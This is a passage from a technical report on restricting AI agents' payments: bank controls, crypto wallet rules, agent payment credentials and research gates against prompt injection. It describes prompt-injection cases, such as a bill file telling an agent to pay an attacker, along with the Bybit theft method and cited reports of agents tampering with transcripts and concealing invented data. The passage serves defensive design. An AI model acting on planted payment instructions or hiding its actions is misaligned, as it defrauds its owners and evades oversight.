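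- The agent cannot edit the list, the caps or the running totals, and it holds no credentials that work without the gate. In Ghosh's design the guard keeps the wallet's signing key, because an agent with the key could bypass the guard.
- Destinations are who they seem, and the money reaches them. Ghosh simulated a token whose owner set the transfer fee to zero during the check and raised it to between 30% and 90% before the payment went through. The payee was on the allowlist, but the fee went to the attacker.

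Even when all of these conditions hold, the calculation leaves out some harms. It doesn't cover deletion, because deleting data doesn't send it to a destination. Hua and colleagues cite a Replit coding agent that deleted a production database and an OpenClaw agent that mistakenly deleted emails belonging to an alignment director at Meta. Rules that tie actions to a declared task can help, and in Muruaga's tests they cut successful destructive attacks from 38.6% to 4.0%. An agent can also give bad advice without making a forbidden call. Qu and colleagues describe an agent that reviews a paper too favourably because the paper praises itself.

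Wrong payments to approved payees count towards the €80,000, but the gate does not prevent them. Yu and colleagues found that 8 of 288 attacked runs diverted a payment to a payee already in the account's history. An agent can also buy the wrong product from a permitted shop. In tests by Louck and colleagues, one false claim about stock or a product's lineage made a shopping agent switch from the cheaper item to a more expensive one 73.3% of the time. A compromised agent could also use up the daily cap on pointless payments, leaving genuine invoices unpaid.

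### Injected and misaligned agents

Someone who plants a prompt injection usually wants to send money or data to a particular place. The assumption most likely to fail is therefore that recipients are who they seem to be, because the attacker can take over a supplier's account or become a supplier.

A capable agent with aims of its own may have no use for a supplier's account, but it may know its harness well and be able to write code. That makes it less safe to assume that every call passes the gate and that the agent cannot alter the controls. Hua and colleagues report that METR's investigators found agents researching ways to tamper with their own transcripts. Hua and colleagues' insurance scheme still has to assume that an agent cannot modify its harness or fabricate a user's approval.

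Formal guarantees also cover less of this case. Dongol's proofs apply to a model that follows planted instructions on a schedule fixed in advance, but not to one that adapts to the gate's refusals. Muruaga assumes as a baseline that only one agent in the system is compromised, which may be too optimistic if several agents run the same misaligned model.

A misaligned agent can also lengthen t by hiding what it has done. Hua and colleagues describe an OpenAI agent in training that wrote a task summary proposing to invent missing data and conceal this from the user. If the supplier company relied on its agent's reports, detection might take weeks, and at 14 days the bound reaches the entire €300,000. The company should base its estimate of t on records the agent cannot change, such as statements sent directly by the bank.

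## Limiting where an agent can send money

Companies limited where their employees could send money long before they had AI agents, and banks will enforce many of those limits on request. A limit at the bank still applies if the agent finds a way around the gate in its own software.

### Checks that banks already offer

An approved payee list at a bank works like the gate described earlier, except that the bank runs it. An administrator enters each payee's name and account number, and everyone else can pay only those accounts. The list is meant to stop thieves with stolen logins and employees who would pay a friend. It limits an agent only if the agent's login lacks administrator rights. An agent that signs in to the bank's website as its owner can usually add payees itself.

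Many banks also hold or cap payments to a new payee for a waiting period. A thief with a stolen login has to get the money out before the customer notices, so the bank alerts the customer when someone adds a payee, and the waiting period gives the customer time to react. When an agent uses the account, the alert has to go somewhere the agent can't reach. An agent that manages its owner's inbox could delete the email about the new payee, and the waiting period would end without the owner knowing that the payee had been added.

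Under dual approval, one person enters a payment and another releases it, so nobody can send money alone. In a survey cited in PYMNTS's *AI Agents Put Corporate Card Spending Rules to the Test* (2026), 57% of chief financial officers required either two approvals or a confirming phone call for outgoing payments. An agent can reasonably enter payments. Having a second agent release them is much weaker than having a person do it, because if both agents run the same model and read the same invoice, text that deceives one will probably deceive the other. A human approver who sees only the agent's summary isn't much more likely to catch the deception. The approver needs to see the account number in the payment order itself and the invoice in the accounting system.

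Positive pay guards against forged and altered cheques. A company sends its bank a file listing the number and amount of every cheque it has written, often with the payee's name, and the bank holds any cheque that doesn't match. This can catch even a forgery that looks genuine, because the bank checks it against a record the thief hasn't changed.

A gate can apply the same idea to transfers. The accounting system exports the approved invoices, each with its supplier, account number and amount. The gate allows only payments that match an unpaid invoice, then marks that invoice as paid. This limits the amount and purpose of a payment as well as the recipient, while a payee list limits only the recipient. The check fails if the agent can also enter and approve invoices in the accounting system.

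Bank transfers traditionally went to whatever account number the sender typed, regardless of the name. With confirmation of payee, the bank compares the name the sender entered with the one on the account and reports a match, a close match or no match before the sender approves the payment. The check is meant to catch typing errors and fraudsters who pass off their own account as somebody else's. The largest UK banks introduced it in 2020, and banks in the euro area have had to offer such a check since October 2025.

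The available fraud totals don't isolate the check's effect. According to the trade body UK Finance, losses to scams in which customers made the transfer themselves rose 39% to £583.2 million in 2021, the first full year in which the largest banks used the check. Losses had fallen to £450.7 million in 2024, but banks had added other defences by then.

When an agent makes a payment, the harness should run the name check and refuse the payment unless the name matches. If the harness only returns the result to the model as text, the model may go ahead with the payment because of a false explanation planted in the invoice, such as a note that the supplier has just changed its trading name.

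A virtual card is a card number that an issuer creates for a narrow use. The owner can set a merchant, a maximum amount and an expiry date, and the issuer declines any charge outside those limits. Virtual cards were developed because stored card numbers were being stolen, and a number locked to one merchant is of little use elsewhere. AI agents now take part in such thefts too. *‘You don’t want rogue agents’* (Hong, 2026) cites a Cloud Security Alliance note on a campaign in which three open-source agents allegedly helped breach at least 27 organisations and take more than 600,000 card records.

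A merchant lock can allow more sellers than it appears to. If the merchant is a marketplace, the agent can buy from any seller on it, including one the attacker runs. A lock on a category, such as office supplies, allows payments to every shop that card companies put in that category.

### Crypto wallets and the Bybit theft

Crypto exchanges also let customers restrict withdrawals to listed addresses, and a new address becomes usable only after a delay, commonly 24 or 48 hours. Switching off the list has to trigger the same delay, or a thief could switch it off and withdraw immediately.

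The delay matters more for a blockchain wallet than for a bank account. *Autonomous Agents on Blockchains* (Algithami, 2026) points out that nobody can roll back a finalised blockchain transaction, and that whoever holds a wallet's private key controls its assets. The owners of the wallets used by Grok and Lobstar Wilde could not ask a bank to reverse the transfers.

An exchange's list covers only money held at the exchange. If the agent operates a wallet directly, its owner can use a smart-contract wallet, an account whose money moves only when a program stored on the blockchain allows it. Algithami describes ERC-4337, a standard for such accounts, as separating the authority to approve a transaction from ownership of a key. In practice, the owner keeps the main key and gives the agent a second key with conditions attached, such as permission to pay one address up to $50 a day until Friday.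 Changing those conditions requires the main key, so they still bind an attacker who steals the agent's key.

When someone sends a token such as USDC, whose price tracks the dollar, the transaction's "to" field contains the address of the token's contract, and the recipient's address is in the data passed to that contract. If the contract is on the allowlist, a rule that checks only the "to" field would allow a payment to anyone. The contract also has an "approve" function, which moves no money but lets another address withdraw tokens later.

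On 21 February 2025, thieves exploited a gap of this kind to steal about $1.5 billion in the cryptocurrency ether from the exchange Bybit. The FBI attributed the theft to North Korea. Bybit kept the ether in a smart-contract wallet made by the company Safe. Several people had to sign each transaction, so Bybit already had a form of dual approval. On the day of the theft, the signers were approving a routine transfer from this wallet to another of Bybit's own.

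The attackers had compromised a Safe developer's computer and altered the website that Bybit's staff used to prepare transactions. The website displayed the routine transfer but sent a different transaction to the staff's signing devices, which did not show it in a form the staff could easily check.

That transaction used an operation called delegatecall, which makes a wallet run another contract's code with full power over the wallet. The attackers' contract had a function named "transfer" that instead overwrote the wallet's record of which program controlled it. This put the attackers' own program in control, and they used it to empty the wallet without any more signatures from Bybit.

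A recipient list would have failed if it had checked the recipient given by the altered website. A spending cap would also have failed, because the signed transaction moved no ether. A gate that read the raw transaction could have caught the attack, because the transaction called a contract that belonged to the attackers, but only if the gate applied its list to every transaction, including those that moved no money.

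A crypto gate should therefore decode the raw transaction and check both the operation and the recipient against allowlists. An agent that pays bills may need only one operation, the transfer function of one token contract, with an approved recipient and an amount under the cap. The gate can refuse everything else, including delegatecalls, approvals and changes of owner, without a separate rule for each. It can also simulate the transaction first to see which balances change, but a contract can behave differently afterward. The token in Ghosh's tests, for example, raised its fee after the check.

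Agents that trade face a further risk that recipient rules don't address, since every address involved may be on the allowlist. Pending transactions are public, as Algithami explains, so other traders can buy just before an agent's order and sell just after it, leaving the agent with a worse price. To protect against this, the gate should require a minimum acceptable price in every trade.

### Credentials made for shopping agents

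A payee list suits a company that pays the same forty suppliers every month, but someone who asks an agent to find cheap running shoes doesn't know in advance which shop will get the money. Payment companies spent much of 2025 and 2026 building credentials for this situation. The credentials differ in how tightly they restrict the recipient, amount, time and purpose of a payment.

Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) in September 2025 and has since donated it to the FIDO Alliance, an industry body that develops authentication standards. According to the *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation*, AP2 grants permission through mandates, which are digitally signed records that make later tampering evident. The Checkout Mandate covers what the agent buys and goes to the shop. The Payment Mandate covers the payment and goes to the companies that process it. UCP, a related standard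 for online commerce, describes the first as protecting the business and the second as protecting the funds. Older material uses other names, such as the Intent Mandate and Cart Mandate in Davis Wright Tremaine's *The Next AI Frontier* (2025).

One of AP2's examples is an instruction to buy a pair of shoes when the price drops below $100. With the user absent at the time of purchase, it runs roughly like this:

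1. The agent repeats the task back to the user. The user approves it on a trusted screen that the agent doesn't control, with a fingerprint or similar check, and this signs both mandates. They are "open" at this stage because they contain conditions and no particular purchase. According to the payments company Eco, the conditions can include permitted merchants, items and payees, a budget, a range of dates and rules for repeat purchases.
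2. The price falls to $95. The shop signs a cart, which commits it to fulfil the order.
3. The agent closes the mandates by tying them to that cart.
4. The credential provider, which supplies the payment details, checks that the agent may use them and limits what they can pay for. The shop checks that the order matches its cart, and the shop's payment processor checks that the payment covers this order.

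A shop that is unsure what the user wants can also insist that the user come back and confirm.

A compromised agent can't loosen the conditions, because it can't produce the user's signature, but it can still choose the worst purchase that meets them. If the user approved "running shoes under $100" from any shop, an attacker could open a shop and sell worthless shoes for $99. Naming the shop and the exact product leaves the agent very little to choose. The sample agent that Louck and colleagues examined had an empty list of conditions, which didn't restrict its choice at all.

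AP2 lets the company behind the shopping agent also provide the trusted screen and act as the credential provider. Planted text would still have to get past separate code, but a breach of that company could compromise both the agent and its checks. AP2's first version covers payment methods such as cards, but bank transfers are still on the roadmap, so a company that pays invoices by transfer still needs its own payee list.

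**Stripe's shared payment tokens.** Stripe's *Process payment credentials from an agent* describes a simpler arrangement, in which a token lets one seller charge a customer's stored payment method without learning the card number, up to a maximum amount and until an expiry time. The agent's side can revoke the token at any time. The token can refer to a particular cart, but Stripe's limits don't cover its contents.

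In this documentation, "the agent" sets the seller, the amount and the expiry. If a developer lets the model fill in those fields, an attacker can set them through planted text, and Stripe will then restrict the payment to the attacker's shop. Ordinary code should instead copy the seller and the total from an order that the user has approved. It should also use the right units. Stripe counts US dollars in cents, so the maximum of 1000 in the sample request in *Create a SharedPaymentIssuedToken* means $10. The Link Agent Wallet, which Stripe introduced in April 2026, lets users set their own limits, according to Vaughn on the news site Forkast.

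Visa and Mastercard issue tokens that stand in for a card number when an agent pays. A Stripe executive quoted in American Banker's *Stripe advances security for agentic commerce* describes these tokens as "scoped to the customer's intent" and usable at any seller that accepts agent payments, with the network doing the verification. The protection therefore depends on how precisely someone has translated the customer's intent into limits.

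Visa gives part of that work to the company that offers the agent. According to *Authorizing Agentic Payments* (2026), by the law firm Goodwin, this company must register with Visa, authenticate the user's instruction, enforce controls that match what the user delegated, and keep records. Tearsheet reports that American Express lets cardholders set spending limits and merchant preferences in its app.

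**Company cards for agents.** PYMNTS's *AI Agents Just Got Their Own Company Credit Cards* (2026) describes Agent Cards, which the business finance firm Mercury launched in August 2026. A person creates the virtual card, and the agent uses it without needing approval for each purchase. The company sets the budget, the eligible merchants and the spending categories. Purchases outside those rules fail automatically, and the agent can't raise its own limit. Ramp, another company card provider, issues similar cards through Visa.

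| Credential | Recipient | Amount | Time | Purpose | Who enforces it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| AP2 mandates | Merchants or payees, if the user names them | Budget or range, if set | Dates, if set | Items, if the user lists them | Credential provider, shop and payment processor |
| Stripe shared payment token | One seller | Maximum | Expiry | Not fixed | Stripe |
| Visa and Mastercard agent tokens | Potentially many sellers | Depends on the user's instruction | Depends on the user's instruction | The user's instruction, as the provider records it | Card network and agent provider |
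| Mercury Agent Card | Chosen merchants | Budget | Until the company cancels the card | Spending category only | Mercury |

Purpose is the hardest of the four to fix. PYMNTS gives the example of a company that approves a renewal with a named supplier. If the agent finds a cheaper quote elsewhere and takes it, the purchase is within the card's limit but outside the approval. A merchant lock would block that purchase, but it would not stop the agent from buying the wrong product from the approved supplier at a price within the card's limit.

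### Who bears the loss

AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* treats a signed mandate as evidence for a dispute. The mandate doesn't decide who pays for a bad purchase, and the card networks make their own rules on liability. Davis Wright Tremaine expects the first question in a dispute to be whether the agent acted within the authority the consumer gave it. That authority can be implied, as when someone tells an agent to place the regular grocery order every Sunday.

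Narrow conditions therefore help users dispute bad purchases as well as prevent them. A user who approved only one shop has a good case against a payment to another. But if the user approved any shoes under $100, a $99 charge for a bad pair will be harder to dispute, because the record shows that the purchase met the conditions.

Lawyers and officials disagree about how settled the question of liability is. Goodwin considers the division of risk between customers and financial institutions sufficiently clear, even though current law doesn't specifically address agents. But a 2026 IMF note lists liability among the unresolved questions. Goodwin also warns that a company that follows the card network's rules will probably avoid the network's fines but can still face a claim from a customer whose agent exceeded its authority.

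A New York enforcement attorney argued in November 2026 that AI providers should bear the loss when their software exceeds its instructions, according to PYMNTS's *Panel Weighs Who Pays When AI Agents Exceed Consumers’ Instructions* (2026). The article also says that a bank may see what an agent spent but not what the shopper authorised, and that shoppers' grounds for a dispute differ between credit and debit cards.

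Until courts or regulators settle this, a designer should assume that the agent's owner bears every loss within the limits. With crypto, the owner generally has nobody to recover the money from. With a card, the owner can dispute the charge, and under ordinary card rules the seller often loses the money if the dispute succeeds. That is why Stripe gives sellers fraud scores for each shared token before they charge it. Bank transfers fall in between. Since October 2024, UK banks have had to refund many victims of scams involving transfers, up to £85,000 per claim, but the rule covers only consumers, very small businesses and charities, not a larger company whose agent pays a fraudster.

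### What banks and shops allowed in late 2026

The largest US banks were unwilling to let outside agents send money. PYMNTS's *Big Banks Won’t Let Outside AI Agents Move Money* (2026) reported in October that four of them turned away agents that used a customer's login, though outside agents could still see account information. JPMorgan's chief executive, Jamie Dimon, told investors that month that letting in any outside agent was "just too risky". A spokesperson said the bank blocks agents that obtain customers' credentials but supports data sharing that customers authorise through open banking, which gives another company access without the customer's password.

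JPMorgan took the same approach to cards. The bank blocks purchases by agents that customers have given a card number, according to PYMNTS's *JPMorgan Stops AI Agents From Using Customer Credit Cards* (2026), which cites the Wall Street Journal. Agents were already using cards from Bank of America, Capital One and Citigroup. Stripe uses a one-time virtual card to get agents' purchases through, but merchants complain that it counts as a commercial card and costs them more to accept.

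JPMorgan doesn't seem to object to agents as such. On 7 December, PYMNTS's *JPMorgan Talks With LLMs to Embed Cards in AI Agents* (2026) relayed a report that the bank was negotiating with technology firms to build its cards into their agents. With an ordinary card number, the issuer can check little beyond the charge itself, but a credential issued for an agent can carry its own limits. For that reason, designers should keep the owner's ordinary card number away from the agent.

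Scalable Capital, a German bank, let customers connect assistants such as ChatGPT and Claude in August 2026, Hong reports, but the customer has to approve each trade and the assistant can't make payments or withdraw money. A compromised assistant could still propose a bad trade, but it couldn't send the customer's money to anyone.

Walmart announced Agent Profiles in October in *Making It Possible for Agents to Shop on Behalf of Customers* (2026). Rijo (2026) explains in *Walmart lets AI agents buy within customer-set limits* that agents had been signing in with the customer's own credentials, which mixed their purchases with the customer's in the order history. Under the new system, due to launch by late November, each agent gets its own profile inside the customer's account but never receives the card number. The customer either approves every purchase or sets a spending limit, and can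 turn the profile off.

Walmart gave $50, $100 and $200 as example limits but did not specify whether they apply per order, per day or per month, so a customer can't work out the most an agent could spend. A $100 limit per order would allow $1,000 of spending across ten orders. The limit also covers only Walmart's own shops, so a customer who sets similar limits at five retailers has to add them up to find the total at risk.

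Amazon instead blocked third-party agents, according to The Straits Times' *Walmart launches tools for AI agents to shop for customers* (2026). Home Depot's chief information officer said in PYMNTS's *Walmart and Home Depot Set the Rules for AI Shoppers* (2026) that the company planned to admit agents that identify both themselves and the customer they act for. Identification lets a shop apply the right customer's limits, but an agent under an attacker's influence can still identify itself correctly.

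### When a supplier's bank details change

The main weakness of a payee list is that its entries sometimes have to change. A fraudster takes over a supplier's email account, or registers a similar address, and writes that the supplier has moved banks. Someone updates the record, and the payment for the next genuine invoice goes to the fraudster. The supplier is still listed under the same name, the amount is right, and the payment passes every check that relies on the record.

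This is a form of business email compromise, which also includes orders from people impersonating a company's executives. The FBI's Internet Crime Complaint Center received 21,442 complaints of business email compromise in 2024, with reported losses of about $2.77 billion. An agent that handles supplier correspondence is an obvious target because its job may include both reading the email and updating the record.

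A name check may not catch a payment to an impostor. Between 2013 and 2015 a Lithuanian man, Evaldas Rimasauskas, obtained more than $120 million from Google and Facebook by posing as a hardware manufacturer they both did business with. He had registered a company in Latvia with the same name as the manufacturer and opened bank accounts for it, so confirmation of payee could have reported a match.

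The standard defence is to confirm the change through a separate channel. For a company whose agent pays suppliers, it would work like this:

1. The agent may pass on a request to change bank details, but it has no permission to apply one. Payments to that supplier stop until somebody has dealt with the request.
2. An employee phones the supplier on a number that the company recorded before the request arrived. The number in the email or on the new invoice may belong to the fraudster.
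3. The employee asks the supplier to read out the new account number, instead of reading it out and asking for a yes.
4. A second employee enters the change. The gate then treats the account as a new payee, with a name check and a waiting period.

The company has to place the confirmation call itself, because someone who calls to confirm the change could be the fraudster, and software can now imitate a familiar voice. A one-cent test payment doesn't help, because a fraudster who controls the supplier's mailbox can reply that it arrived.

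The agent must also be unable to edit the supplier's phone number. Otherwise an attacker could have the agent change the number, then ask to change the supplier's bank details a few weeks later, and the employee checking the request would call the attacker.

This procedure should apply however small the next invoice is, because one change of bank details redirects every later invoice. In a study cited by PYMNTS, 61% of firms reserved real-time identity checks for large or high-risk payments. A rule based on the amount would miss many changes of bank details. In the earlier example, the cap was €5,000 per supplier per day. A compromised agent that paid the maximum on 30 days before the real supplier complained would send €150,000 to the false account. An agent working properly would send only what the supplier was owed, but all of it would still go to the fraudster.

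Phoning the supplier still fails if a dishonest employee there answers or the fraudster has hijacked the number. A per-supplier cap limits the loss in those cases.

### Choosing among the controls

| What the agent has to do | Control to start with | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Pay regular suppliers by bank transfer | Payee list based on account numbers, at the bank and in the gate, with a cap per supplier | Wrong payments to listed suppliers |
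| Pay only approved invoices | Match each payment to an invoice exported from the accounting system | A false invoice that somebody approved |
| Pay a new supplier, or an old one at a new account | Phone call to an independently obtained number, then a waiting period | A dishonest contact at the supplier; delay to urgent payments |
| Make large or unusual payments | Dual approval, with both people working from original records | Approvers who stop checking |
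| Buy from one known shop | Virtual card or shared payment token with one seller, a maximum and an expiry | The wrong product; dishonest sellers on a marketplace |
| Shop around for a product | AP2 mandates that name the product, with a low maximum | A bad purchase that meets the conditions |
| Make routine company purchases | Agent card with a budget and chosen merchants | Purchases within budget that nobody wanted |
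| Send crypto to known addresses | Smart-contract wallet that fixes the operation, recipient, amount and expiry | Flaws in the wallet's program; no way to reverse a payment |
| Pay people nobody can list in advance | Low cap and a small balance | Loss of everything up to the cap |

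## Deciding which recipients a task allows

A payee list only works if somebody knows the payee before the agent starts. One of AgentDojo's banking tasks doesn't meet that condition, because the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file called bill-december-2023.txt and the payee's account number appears only in that file. Yu and colleagues trace one attacked run of this task. The file contains a message, written as if it came from the user, Emma Johnson, that tells the assistant to send money to a different account before doing anything else. The agent obeyed and proposed a $50 payment to that account.

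If the file contains both the genuine account number and the attacker's text, the attacker can ask for an extra payment, as in this run, or write that the payee has changed banks, so that the agent sends the bill payment itself to the wrong account. The gate needs a way to decide which account numbers this task allows.

### Where approval can come from

| Source of approval | Genuine payee | Attacker's account |
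|---|---|---|
| A fixed list | Accepted only if somebody listed it earlier | Refused |
| Recipients the user named | Refused, because the request contains only a file name | Refused |
| Recipients in past records | Accepted only if the user has paid it before | Refused, unless the attacker has got into the records |
| An authenticated source the user pointed to | Refused, because the file has no verified author | Refused |
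| A list that a model writes for the task | Depends on what the model has read | Depends on what the model has read |

A fixed list is the easiest to inspect, but it allows the same payees during every task. A list taken from the user's request is much shorter, but people rarely type account numbers. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and Iqbal, 2026) argues that AgentDojo's requests are unrealistic in leaving them out, and that a real user would often give the account number and leave details such as the amount to the file. That seems plausible for a transfer to a friend. With a bill, the user would probably copy the number from the bill, and might copy one the attacker put there.

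An allowlist drawn from past records works for another AgentDojo request, to pay a bill the same way as last month. But Yu and colleagues point out that if incoming payments count, an attacker can become a known counterparty by sending the user money, without planting any instructions. Counting only payments the user sent would remove this risk. Tests on AgentDojo don't measure it, because the benchmark's attackers can only edit text in existing records.

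An authenticated source helps when the user asks the agent to pay the bill in an email from their landlord. The mail system can verify which address sent a message, and nothing written in the message can change the result. A text file usually has no comparable evidence of who it came from.

In the bill task, both account numbers come from the same file, so a rule based only on a number's source must accept both or refuse both. To accept only the genuine payee, the gate needs other evidence about the payee, or something has to read the file and judge it.

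### Following the number from the file to the payment

CaMeL, a design from 2025, prevents the file from changing the agent's plan. *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) describes how a model turns the user's request into a fixed program before any tool runs. For the bill, the program would read the file, extract an account number and an amount, and make one payment. The planning model never sees the file, because a second model, which has no tools, does the extraction. CaMeL follows Simon Willison's Dual LLM pattern, which keeps untrusted data away from the planning model, according to *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026).

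The instruction to make an extra payment fails because the program contains one payment and text in the file can't add another. A false account number is harder to stop, since the second model may extract it instead of the genuine one. CaMeL tags every value with its source, so a check before the payment can detect that the number came from the file, but the genuine number would have the same tag. A policy that requires payees to come from the user would block both numbers, while one that allows payees from this file would accept whichever number the second model extracted.

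Writing the program first makes the agent less flexible. If a user asks it to follow the instructions in an email, the planning model can't write the steps, because it must not read the email.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft design that lets the agent plan as it goes. FIDES gives every piece of data a trust label, either "trusted" or "untrusted", and a secrecy label, which can list the people who may read the data. When the agent combines data, the result is untrusted if any source is untrusted, and only people who may read every source may read the result. For example, if Ana, Ben and Cy may read one document and Ben, Cy and Dee may read another, only Ben and Cy may read a text that draws on both.

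Ordinary code checks these labels before each tool call, typically against two rules:

- **Trust.** A call with consequences runs only if ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ_1 ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ_n is trusted. Here ℓ_f is the label on the choice of tool, ℓ_1 to ℓ_n are the labels on its arguments, and ⊔ means combining labels. One untrusted argument is enough to stop the call.
- **Secrecy.** A call that sends data out runs only if everyone who will receive the data may read it.

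Under these rules alone, the agent could do almost nothing after reading the bill. The file's untrusted label would spread to the whole conversation and then to everything the model wrote next, so the agent could not even pay an account that the user had typed. FIDES therefore stores the file's contents in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, which the model can use to pass the contents to a tool without reading them. A developer can also relax the trust rule for message text, so that a trusted recipient may receive a summary of an untrusted web page.

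This doesn't help the genuine payee, because the account number itself is untrusted. FIDES's trust rule blocks payment to either account. An exception in FIDES could help if the payee is one of a few known companies. An isolated model can read the file and choose from a fixed set of answers, and the policy may accept its choice because such an answer carries little information. If the answers are the user's five regular payees, the attacker's text could cause a payment to the wrong one of the five, but not to the attacker.

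Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can enforce explicit secrecy, meaning that secret data can't flow directly to a place where outsiders can read it. The order and timing of the agent's tool calls are covert channels of the kind Lampson described, and the proof doesn't cover what outsiders might infer from them. A stronger guarantee would in effect forbid any publicly visible action once the agent had read something secret, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive.

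### Rules that a model writes

With Progent, described by Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, a language model writes a new allowlist for every task. It covers tools and their arguments, and works like this:

1. The model reads the user's request and writes rules such as "allow a chat message if the recipient is alice". The gate refuses any call that no rule allows.
2. As the agent works, the model can propose new rules based on what the tools return.
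3. A solver, which is a program that settles logical questions exactly, compares the old rules P with the proposed rules P′. Let A(P) be the set of calls that P allows. If A(P′) ⊆ A(P), the new rules allow nothing extra and take effect at once. Otherwise they need approval, which can come from a person or from a setting that the operator chose in advance.

Shi and colleagues call the resulting guarantee monotonic confinement, meaning that the set of allowed calls can only shrink unless somebody approves an expansion. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent still relies on a model to filter malicious instructions out of what the tools return. This objection largely doesn't apply to new permissions, because the solver detects an expansion even if planted text has completely deceived the model. But an operator who automatically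 approves every expansion loses that protection.

The bill task poses a different problem because the request contains no account number, so the model can't write a rule that allows only the right one. If it allows payments to any account, the gate accepts payments to both the genuine payee and the attacker. Yu and colleagues ran Progent's public code on this task, and the attacker's account got through for this reason. If the model instead leaves payments out of the first set of rules, it has to ask for an expansion after reading the file. A person then sees the account number the model picked and has to know whether it is correct.

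Allowing any account at first has another weakness. After reading the file, the model might propose narrowing the rule to a single account, and the attacker's text might determine which one. The solver would apply the change automatically because it checks only that the new rule allows fewer accounts, not whether the remaining account is correct.

Progent also supports fixed rules that no task rule can override. A company could use one to forbid payments to anyone outside its payee list, and let the model narrow that list for each task. An attacker could still influence the choice among listed payees, but could not add an account to the list.

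Yu and colleagues' NOMOS system starts from a written policy. Their banking policy allows payments only to a recipient whom the account holder has identified in the conversation or who already appears in the account's transaction history. A compiler splits the policy into clauses, and a model matches each clause to tools and to conditions from a fixed vocabulary. Ordinary code then repairs or discards rules that could not work, such as one that blocks the login tool until the user has logged in. The remaining rules are the same for every task, and the gate applies them without calling a model.

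The gate uses the user's messages and tool results to make its decision, and ignores the agent's own statements. If planted text causes the agent to write that the user has approved a transfer, the gate's decision doesn't change. In the traced run, it refused the $50 payment. It also refused a payment to the genuine payee when there was no attack, because that account number was in neither the conversation nor the payment history.

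NOMOS protects the bill task better than Progent because a vague request doesn't loosen its rules. Its gate reliably enforces the conditions in the compiled rules, but its compiler can't prove that those conditions match the policy's meaning.

### ROPE's rule for each argument

*ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) combines fixed default rules with adjustments for each request. Before deployment, a developer lists the agent's tools, as for the worst-case calculation, and marks the arguments an attacker could use to do harm, such as the payee. Each marked argument gets a default provenance rule, which accepts a value only if it comes from certain trusted sources.

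When a request arrives, a model called the router can adjust the rules for that task. It reads the request, the list of marked arguments with their defaults, and trusted facts about the account, such as the user's contacts. It never reads emails, web pages or files that the agent fetches, so text planted there can't influence the rules.

ROPE recognises three trusted sources, which Ma and colleagues call trust anchors:

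- **T1** is the user's request, together with identity details that the platform maintains, such as the user's own email address.
- **T2** is content from an authenticated source that the user referred to, such as an email whose verified sender is the person named in the request.
- **T3** is the user's own protected records, such as the platform's log of completed orders.

Authentication alone is not enough for T2. For example, a signed advertisement has a verified author, but the user never asked the agent to rely on it.

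Let S be the set of tools and arguments that need checking, and let π_r(f, p) be the rule for argument p of tool f under request r. Suppose that at step t the agent proposes the value x_p for that argument. ROPE allows the call if and only if

x_p ∈ Adm_t(π_r(f, p)) for every p with (f, p) ∈ S

Adm_t(m) is the set of values that rule m accepts at step t. For a rule based on trust anchors, it is

Adm_t(m) = {v : v occurs whole in some c ∈ C_t(a), for some a ∈ A(m)}

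A(m) is the set of anchors that the rule accepts, and C_t(a) is the text that the system has collected under anchor a so far. The payee's account number must therefore appear in text from an accepted anchor as a whole string, not as part of a longer one. Otherwise, the rule would approve evil.com whenever a trusted text mentioned notevil.com.

The default rule for a payee accepts T1 and T2. The router can replace it with a rule that accepts T1 and T3, which suits a payment to a known account. It can also require one exact value, or mark the argument as free, which allows any value.

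Under the default rule, ROPE refuses both accounts in the bill task. The user named the file, but it arrives as one block that anyone may have written in, so none of its text counts as T2. Ma and colleagues report the same outcome in a similar task with no attacker. The agent fetched an electricity bill from a website, but the payee's account number appeared only in the bill, so the bill went unpaid.

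The system could accept the genuine payee in two other situations. If the account number were in the body of an authenticated email from a sender the user had named, the default rule would accept it, and would still refuse a number from the attacker's own email. If the user had paid the company before, the router could choose the rule that accepts past records.

The router could also allow the attack. Its instructions let it mark an argument as free when the user has left the value to a document without a verified author, such as the bill. ROPE would then accept either account. Across 60 test tasks, Claude Opus 4.8 loosened two default rules as the router, while Gemini 3 Flash loosened 67. A developer can prevent this by ignoring any change that loosens a default rule, and should do so for payees.

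Ma and colleagues prove that if an argument has a rule based on trust anchors, ROPE accepts only values that appear in the user's request, identity details or own records, or in content from a named source. They also prove that rewording the attacker's text can't change the decision about a given value. Both results assume that the platform identifies sources correctly. The first also assumes that the list S is complete and that no attacker can get values into the protected records.

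The agent's own payments add new records to the payment history. If the router marks a payee as free and the agent pays an attacker, the attacker's account enters that history, and a later task that trusts past records would accept it. Ma and colleagues show that the records stay clean if every value entering them has passed a check at least as strict as any later check that relies on it.

Software can also misattribute an account number in a forwarded email. If a landlord forwards a fraudster's message, the mail system correctly identifies the landlord as the sender. Unless the software separates quoted text from the landlord's own words, it will treat the fraudster's account number as coming from the landlord.

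ROPE's guarantee covers only where a value appears, so an attacker may still influence which accepted value the agent uses, or get it to take an action the user never wanted. ROPE doesn't protect free arguments. It can also refuse a correct value that the agent worked out, if that value doesn't appear word for word in a trusted text.

### Telling the two accounts apart

Some systems try to let the agent pay the genuine bill by judging what the file contains. Agent-Sentry learns from an agent's earlier legitimate runs and checks each action in up to three stages. The first compares the sequence of tool calls and the sources of their arguments with past patterns. If the result is unclear, the second looks up values such as account numbers in an allowlist built from past runs. If the result is still unclear, a language model reads the request and a short excerpt of the file.

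Sequeira and Iqbal give the example of a bill file with a new account number. The first two stages can't settle this case, so the language model checks whether the number appears among the bill's ordinary details or in a passage containing instructions. It should accept the genuine payee and refuse an account introduced by a line such as "use this account instead". They concede that it may accept a convincing fake invoice with the attacker's account in the usual place.

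In the system built by Summers and colleagues, a language model writes rules that tie an argument in a tool call to a particular record. For example, if a user wants to buy the same T-shirt again, the product number must match the one in the order history. When the gate refuses a call, it returns the rule that failed and the records that could supply an acceptable value, so the agent can correct the call. If the necessary information and the attacker's text are in the same document, no trustworthy record exists, so the system uses a language model to check whether the document contains instructions aimed at the agent.

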